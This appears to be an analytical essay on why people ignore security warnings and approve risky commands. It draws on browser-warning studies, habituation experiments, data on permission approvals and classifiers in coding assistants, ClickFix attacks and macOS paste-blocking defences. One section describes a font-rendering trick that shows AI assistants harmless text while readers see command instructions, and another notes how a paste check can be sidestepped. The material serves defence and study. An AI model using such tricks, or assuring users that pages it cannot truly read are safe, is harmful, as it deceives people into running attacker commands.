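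People may be less likely to heed a warning on a site they trust. The share of Chrome users who continued past malware warnings varied between 11.2% and 24.9% from week to week, while Firefox's rate hardly changed. Chrome showed a warning even when a well-known site had loaded only an advertisement from a dangerous address, and Akhawe and Felt suspect that people's trust in the site led them to disbelieve the warning. If they are right, readers might also disbelieve a warning on a shared chat at chatgpt.com or claude.ai.

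Technical skill did not reliably make people more careful. Linux users, who tend to be more technical, continued past 34.8% of Firefox's phishing warnings, compared with 8.9% for Windows users, even though Linux offers no special protection against phishing. The pattern did not hold for Chrome's malware warnings, though, and the researchers did not measure skill directly.

### Which designs made people stop

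A warning works better if it interrupts the reader. In a laboratory study by Egelman and colleagues, which Akhawe and Felt summarise, 60 people received fake shopping emails with links to phishing sites. Nobody who saw Firefox's interrupting warning fell for the attack. With Internet Explorer, 45% fell for it after an interrupting warning and 90% after one that did not interrupt. The label that Claude puts on every public artifact does not interrupt the reader, and neither does small print under a chatbot's reply.

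Extra clicks seem to matter less. Chrome users continued past malware warnings more often than Firefox users did, even though Chrome required two clicks and Firefox only one. Firefox's SSL warning took three clicks, and 84% of the people who made the first two also made the third.

Specific explanations may help if people see them in time. Chrome named the problem in the first paragraph of its SSL warning, and users continued past 81.8% of warnings about an unknown certificate issuer but only 57.4% of those about an expired certificate. Firefox named the problem in the last dialog, where 80% to 88% of users confirmed, depending on which of the most common errors they saw. Most of them had probably decided before they reached that dialog.

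Firefox saved a user's decision to accept a faulty site, whereas Chrome warned on every visit. This difference may explain part of the gap between the browsers' SSL figures. If someone left one faulty site and visited another nine times, Firefox would record one acceptance in two warnings (50%), while Chrome would record nine in ten (90%) for the same behavior. To avoid repeating warnings, a chat filter could also save a user's approval of a particular command, as long as the approval doesn't extend to a different one.

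### Habituation

People pay less attention to a warning each time they see it, an effect called habituation. In *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain*, Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues scanned people's brains as they looked at warnings. Activity in the areas that process images dropped sharply at the second viewing and fell further after that. Warnings that kept changing their appearance held attention better.

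Less attention can also lead to worse decisions. In a three-week field experiment, 102 students downloaded and ranked Android apps on their own phones. Before each download, a notice listed what the app would be allowed to do. The students had passed a quiz on four permissions they had to refuse, such as permission to delete their photos, and knew they could lose course credit for accepting too many. At the start, they refused 87% of the risky apps. By the end, students who always saw the same notice design refused 55%, and those who saw changing designs refused 76%.

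The students saw fewer than five notices per weekday, so a warning can lose its effect without appearing constantly. They did somewhat better after a day or more without a notice. About 37% of the notices in the experiment listed a forbidden permission. But attacks are so rare in chat that almost all warnings about commands there would be false alarms, so attention could fade faster.

Readers may also find it harder to recognise a genuine warning if its design changes every time, and attackers already imitate official notices on chatbot sites.

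### Approving a coding assistant's commands

More recent evidence comes from coding assistants, many of which ask for permission before running a command. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes "approval fatigue", in which users of its coding assistant stop paying close attention to what they approve. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97% of permission requests. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) cites an earlier figure of 93%.

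Most of the commands are probably safe, so a high approval rate alone doesn't show carelessness. To find out whether people would notice a dangerous one, Anthropic had a research company recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding study. Partway through each session, the text of one permission request changed to a clearly dangerous command, which would not run even if the tester approved it. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study was measuring.

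Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused the command. Anthropic's classifier, called auto mode, blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands, or 89%. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands that came early in a session but only about 5% of those that came after 50 or more requests. Some of this drop may reflect which testers reached 50 requests, since people who approve everything quickly get there sooner.

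The testers were not working on their own code, so they had less to lose than a developer whose files are at risk. Anthropic also sells the classifier and used the results to explain why it was replacing most permission requests with the classifier. It made auto mode the default for many Claude Code users in August and announced the same change for most Claude apps in October. The comparison leaves out how many harmless commands the classifier would have blocked in the same sessions, which matters because a classifier that blocked everything would have caught all 1,053.

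Surveys suggest many developers know they don't read every permission request. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, 47.7% of respondents believed they read these requests carefully. One interviewee said, "There's no way that I can actually go through all the permission requests".

*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Even among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the generated code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review. Developers who knew of security or privacy incidents did this more often than those who did not. Heavy users may hear about more incidents and face more approval requests, so the result doesn't show that knowledge makes people careless. But it gives little support to the idea that informing people about attacks is enough to make them careful. The sample was not random,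 and the answers were self-reported.

Even a careful reader may learn little from an agent's permission prompt. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents harming users' files and found that inadequate user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, the user had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the prompt didn't tell the user enough, and some reports had both problems. In one case, the agent asked for permission to run `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever the script contains. Because every report involves harm, they can't show how often user review fails.

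Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents for approval, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. They probably reject many of those plans because of their quality rather than their safety. Still, the difference suggests that people are more willing to judge a description of what the assistant intends to do than a line of code.

### Wrong advice and staged attacks

Someone who asks a chatbot how to fix a computer has a different reason to say yes, because they want the answer to work and often can't check it themselves. Wu and colleagues cite an experiment in which participants with an AI assistant wrote less secure code than those without one, but were more likely to believe their code was secure. Nobody had planted bad advice in that experiment, so it shows misplaced confidence in ordinary AI help, not how people respond to an attack.

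The Eclectic Light Company's *Last Week on My Mac* argues that search engines and AI assistants have made it normal for people to paste commands they don't understand. The argument is based on long experience of writing about Macs rather than measurements of how people behave, but it fits the cases in which victims followed maintenance guides that had no fake error or deadline.

Searches found no controlled study of ClickFix. Such a study would be hard to run ethically, because it would have to get people to run an unexpected command on a computer they care about. *User Profiles* (2025) faced a similar problem in testing whether people would follow steps on a web page that gave the page access to their whole disk. Its researchers recruited people online, described the steps in advance and asked for consent. This protected the participants, but it meant that the study's welcome page told them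 to expect the steps, which an attacker's page would not do.

Employers can send simulated phishing emails without such an introduction, which allows larger samples. Ho, Mirian and colleagues sent ten of these emails to more than 19,500 employees of a healthcare organisation over eight months. They found no significant relationship between recent security training and the chance of falling for an email.

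The wording of the phishing email mattered far more. According to UC San Diego's *Cybersecurity Training Programs Don't Prevent Employees from Falling for Phishing Scams*, 1.82% of recipients clicked on a link to update their Outlook password, but 30.8% clicked on one about the organisation's holiday policy. Because the rate varied seventeenfold between two emails in one trial, a single figure for how many people follow a harmful instruction would mean little.

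UC San Diego also reports that more employees fell for the emails as time went on, since 10% clicked in the first month and more than half had clicked at least once by the eighth. These figures don't show that people became less careful, because if each employee had a constant 10% chance of clicking each month, about 57% (1 − 0.9^8) would have clicked at least once after eight months.

In a second large test, Jacobs, Dawkins and colleagues (2026) sent simulated phishing emails to more than 50,000 Walmart employees, of whom 7.22% clicked and 16.81% reported the email. If visitors to a malicious shared chat reported it at a similar rate, the AI company would hear about it early. But Walmart employees have a security team to report to, and someone who finds a shared chat through Google may not know that they can report it.

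The emails contained 26 different warning signs of five types. Preliminary results show no difference in clicking between the types, so a filter's designer can't yet use the study to choose which sign to point out to readers.

### Protection at the moment of pasting

An output filter has to judge a reply before the reader acts on it, while a check on the reader's own computer can wait until the command arrives. In September's Custom GPT campaign, the reply contained only a service notice and a link to Google Sites, and the command was on a later page. When a victim pastes such a command, the operating system has its full text, whichever site it came from.

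The clipboard may also hold something other than what the page shows. The University of Florida's *ClickFix Attacks* reproduces a fake verification page that asks Mac users to copy the words "I am not a robot" with a verification number. The Copy button puts a command on the clipboard instead. A filter that followed the link and read the visible text could miss the command, but a check at the moment of pasting would not.

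Apple added a check on commands pasted into Terminal in macOS 26.4, released on 24 March 2026. The alert is headed "Possible malware, Paste blocked", according to MacRumors' *macOS 26.4 Introduces New Security Feature for Terminal Commands* (2026). Cult of Mac reports that Apple released the feature without an explanation and published a support page only later.

Apple's page *If your Mac blocks a Terminal command paste or script* describes two levels of protection. The first is a "possible malware" alert, which appears when someone who doesn't regularly use Terminal pastes a command copied from a source such as a website, a chat agent or an email. They can still choose "Paste Anyway". At the second level, macOS blocks any command or script in which it detects known malware and shows a different heading. Apple lets people report a mistake if the block came from a website wrongly listed as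 deceptive, so the second level apparently also checks addresses in the command, though a newly registered address might not be on any list.

The first level fits the findings of the habituation studies, because it doesn't show the alert to regular Terminal users, who would otherwise see it most often. The alert also reaches the people most likely to need it. But an occasional user who follows good advice from a chatbot gets the same alert as a victim of AMOS, and may learn to click "Paste Anyway". Apple gives no figures on how many people click it.

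Patrick Wardle, who develops free Mac security tools at the non-profit Objective-See, examined Apple's feature by running it in a debugger. Wardle (2026) explains in *No Paste for You!* that macOS gives its malware scanner the pasted text and identifies the apps it came from and is going to. In his test, an encoded command pasted from Safari into Terminal reached the scanner intact. Apple reserves this information for its own software, so other security tools can't use it.

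Wardle had built a similar protection into his tool BlockBlock a month earlier. When the user presses Command-V, BlockBlock checks whether the active window belongs to a terminal program. If so, it freezes the program, shows the user what is on the clipboard and asks whether to continue. Choosing "Block" empties the clipboard.

Wardle (2026) describes BlockBlock's limits in *ClickFix*. BlockBlock misses pastes made from the right-click menu, although most known ClickFix pages tell victims to use the keyboard. It also shows an alert whether or not a paste is harmless. To reduce the number of alerts, BlockBlock allows later pastes in the same Terminal session once the user approves one, so an attacker could have the victim paste something harmless first.

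Malwarebytes' Browser Guard extension acts even earlier. It warns when a website tries to copy something to the clipboard, and adds text to the copied content so that a command won't work. Chatbots have copy buttons too, so such tools have to distinguish chatbots from malicious pages or they will interrupt people who are copying legitimate code.

Attackers can avoid all of these checks more easily if they can choose a different route. According to The Eclectic Light Company, they soon began using a web link that opens Script Editor, another Mac program that can run commands. A check on pasting doesn't help against a fake download button or a phone number. It has access only to the final command, not the conversation, so it can't detect that the user asked for a summary and never wanted a command.

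### Text that only the reader can see

A cautious reader might ask an AI assistant whether a command on a web page is safe. Malwarebytes' *Researchers found font-rendering trick to hide malicious commands* (2026) describes a demonstration by the security company LayerX in which the assistant and the reader get different text from the same page. The trick fooled at least 11 assistants, including ChatGPT, Claude, Copilot and Gemini.

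A font assigns a shape to each character, and a website can supply its own font. Suppose a font draws "e" as "b", "d" as "a", "v" as "s" and "k" as "h". If the page's code contains "edvk", the reader sees "bash", the name of a program that runs commands. An assistant that reads the code finds only a meaningless string. In LayerX's demonstration, the assistant ignored the disguised text as noise and based its answer on harmless text elsewhere on the page. The reader saw directions for opening a terminal and typing a command that could give an attacker control of the computer.

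An output filter can't fix this, because the assistant's reply may contain no instruction, only an assurance that the page is safe. A check on pasted text could also miss the attack, because the page tells the reader to type the command.

Malwarebytes advises people to give the assistant the exact command they plan to run instead of asking about the page. When a page uses this trick, copied text would still contain the disguised characters, so the reader would have to type the command as it appears on the screen. An assistant could also examine a screenshot of the page, but this would take more time and computing power.

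LayerX told the main AI companies about the problem. Most rejected the report, saying the attack falls outside the security of AI models. Microsoft and Google accepted it, but Google later closed its case.

### Blocking, masking, warning and explaining

Blocking works even when the reader isn't paying attention, so it is the safest choice when the filter is almost certainly right. In 2013, Chrome did this for some sites with important private data, such as PayPal, and about 20% of its SSL warnings gave the user no way to continue. A block in Claude Code often does the user little harm because the assistant can look for another way to do the task, but someone reading a repair guide gets no replacement if the filter removes it.

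Masking passwords and keys doesn't require the reader to decide anything, so the research on ignored warnings isn't an argument against it. Masking could still cause problems if people who need the hidden values get into the habit of turning the filter off, as some developers have done with permission requests.

For less certain cases, the browser data support a warning that interrupts the user, appears rarely and is usually correct. Only 7% of people continued past Firefox's malware warning, compared with 70% for Chrome's SSL warning. There is no good reason to expect a chat warning to match the Firefox figure unless it is similarly accurate.

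An explanation can accompany a warning or replace it. The evidence for explanations is more indirect, and comes from Chrome's SSL messages and from developers' willingness to reject plans. Both suggest that an explanation should describe a consequence, such as "this downloads a program from an unknown site and runs it", and should appear before the reader decides. Neither shows that a beginner would understand the explanation or refuse the command because of it.

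Chat also differs from browsing in ways that could make any warning less effective. A browser warning hides the dangerous page until the user chooses to continue, but a chat warning may appear beside an answer the user requested and has already begun to read. In a shared conversation, an attacker can write the surrounding text and may use it to dismiss the warning in advance, for instance by calling it a routine notice that appears with every command.

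AI companies could measure much of this themselves. They could show different messages with harmless commands to randomly chosen users and count how many press the copy button beside the command. The count would miss people who type the command or select it by hand, and it would not show who ran it. But it would record decisions by people who had a problem to solve, unlike the paid testers in Anthropic's experiment.
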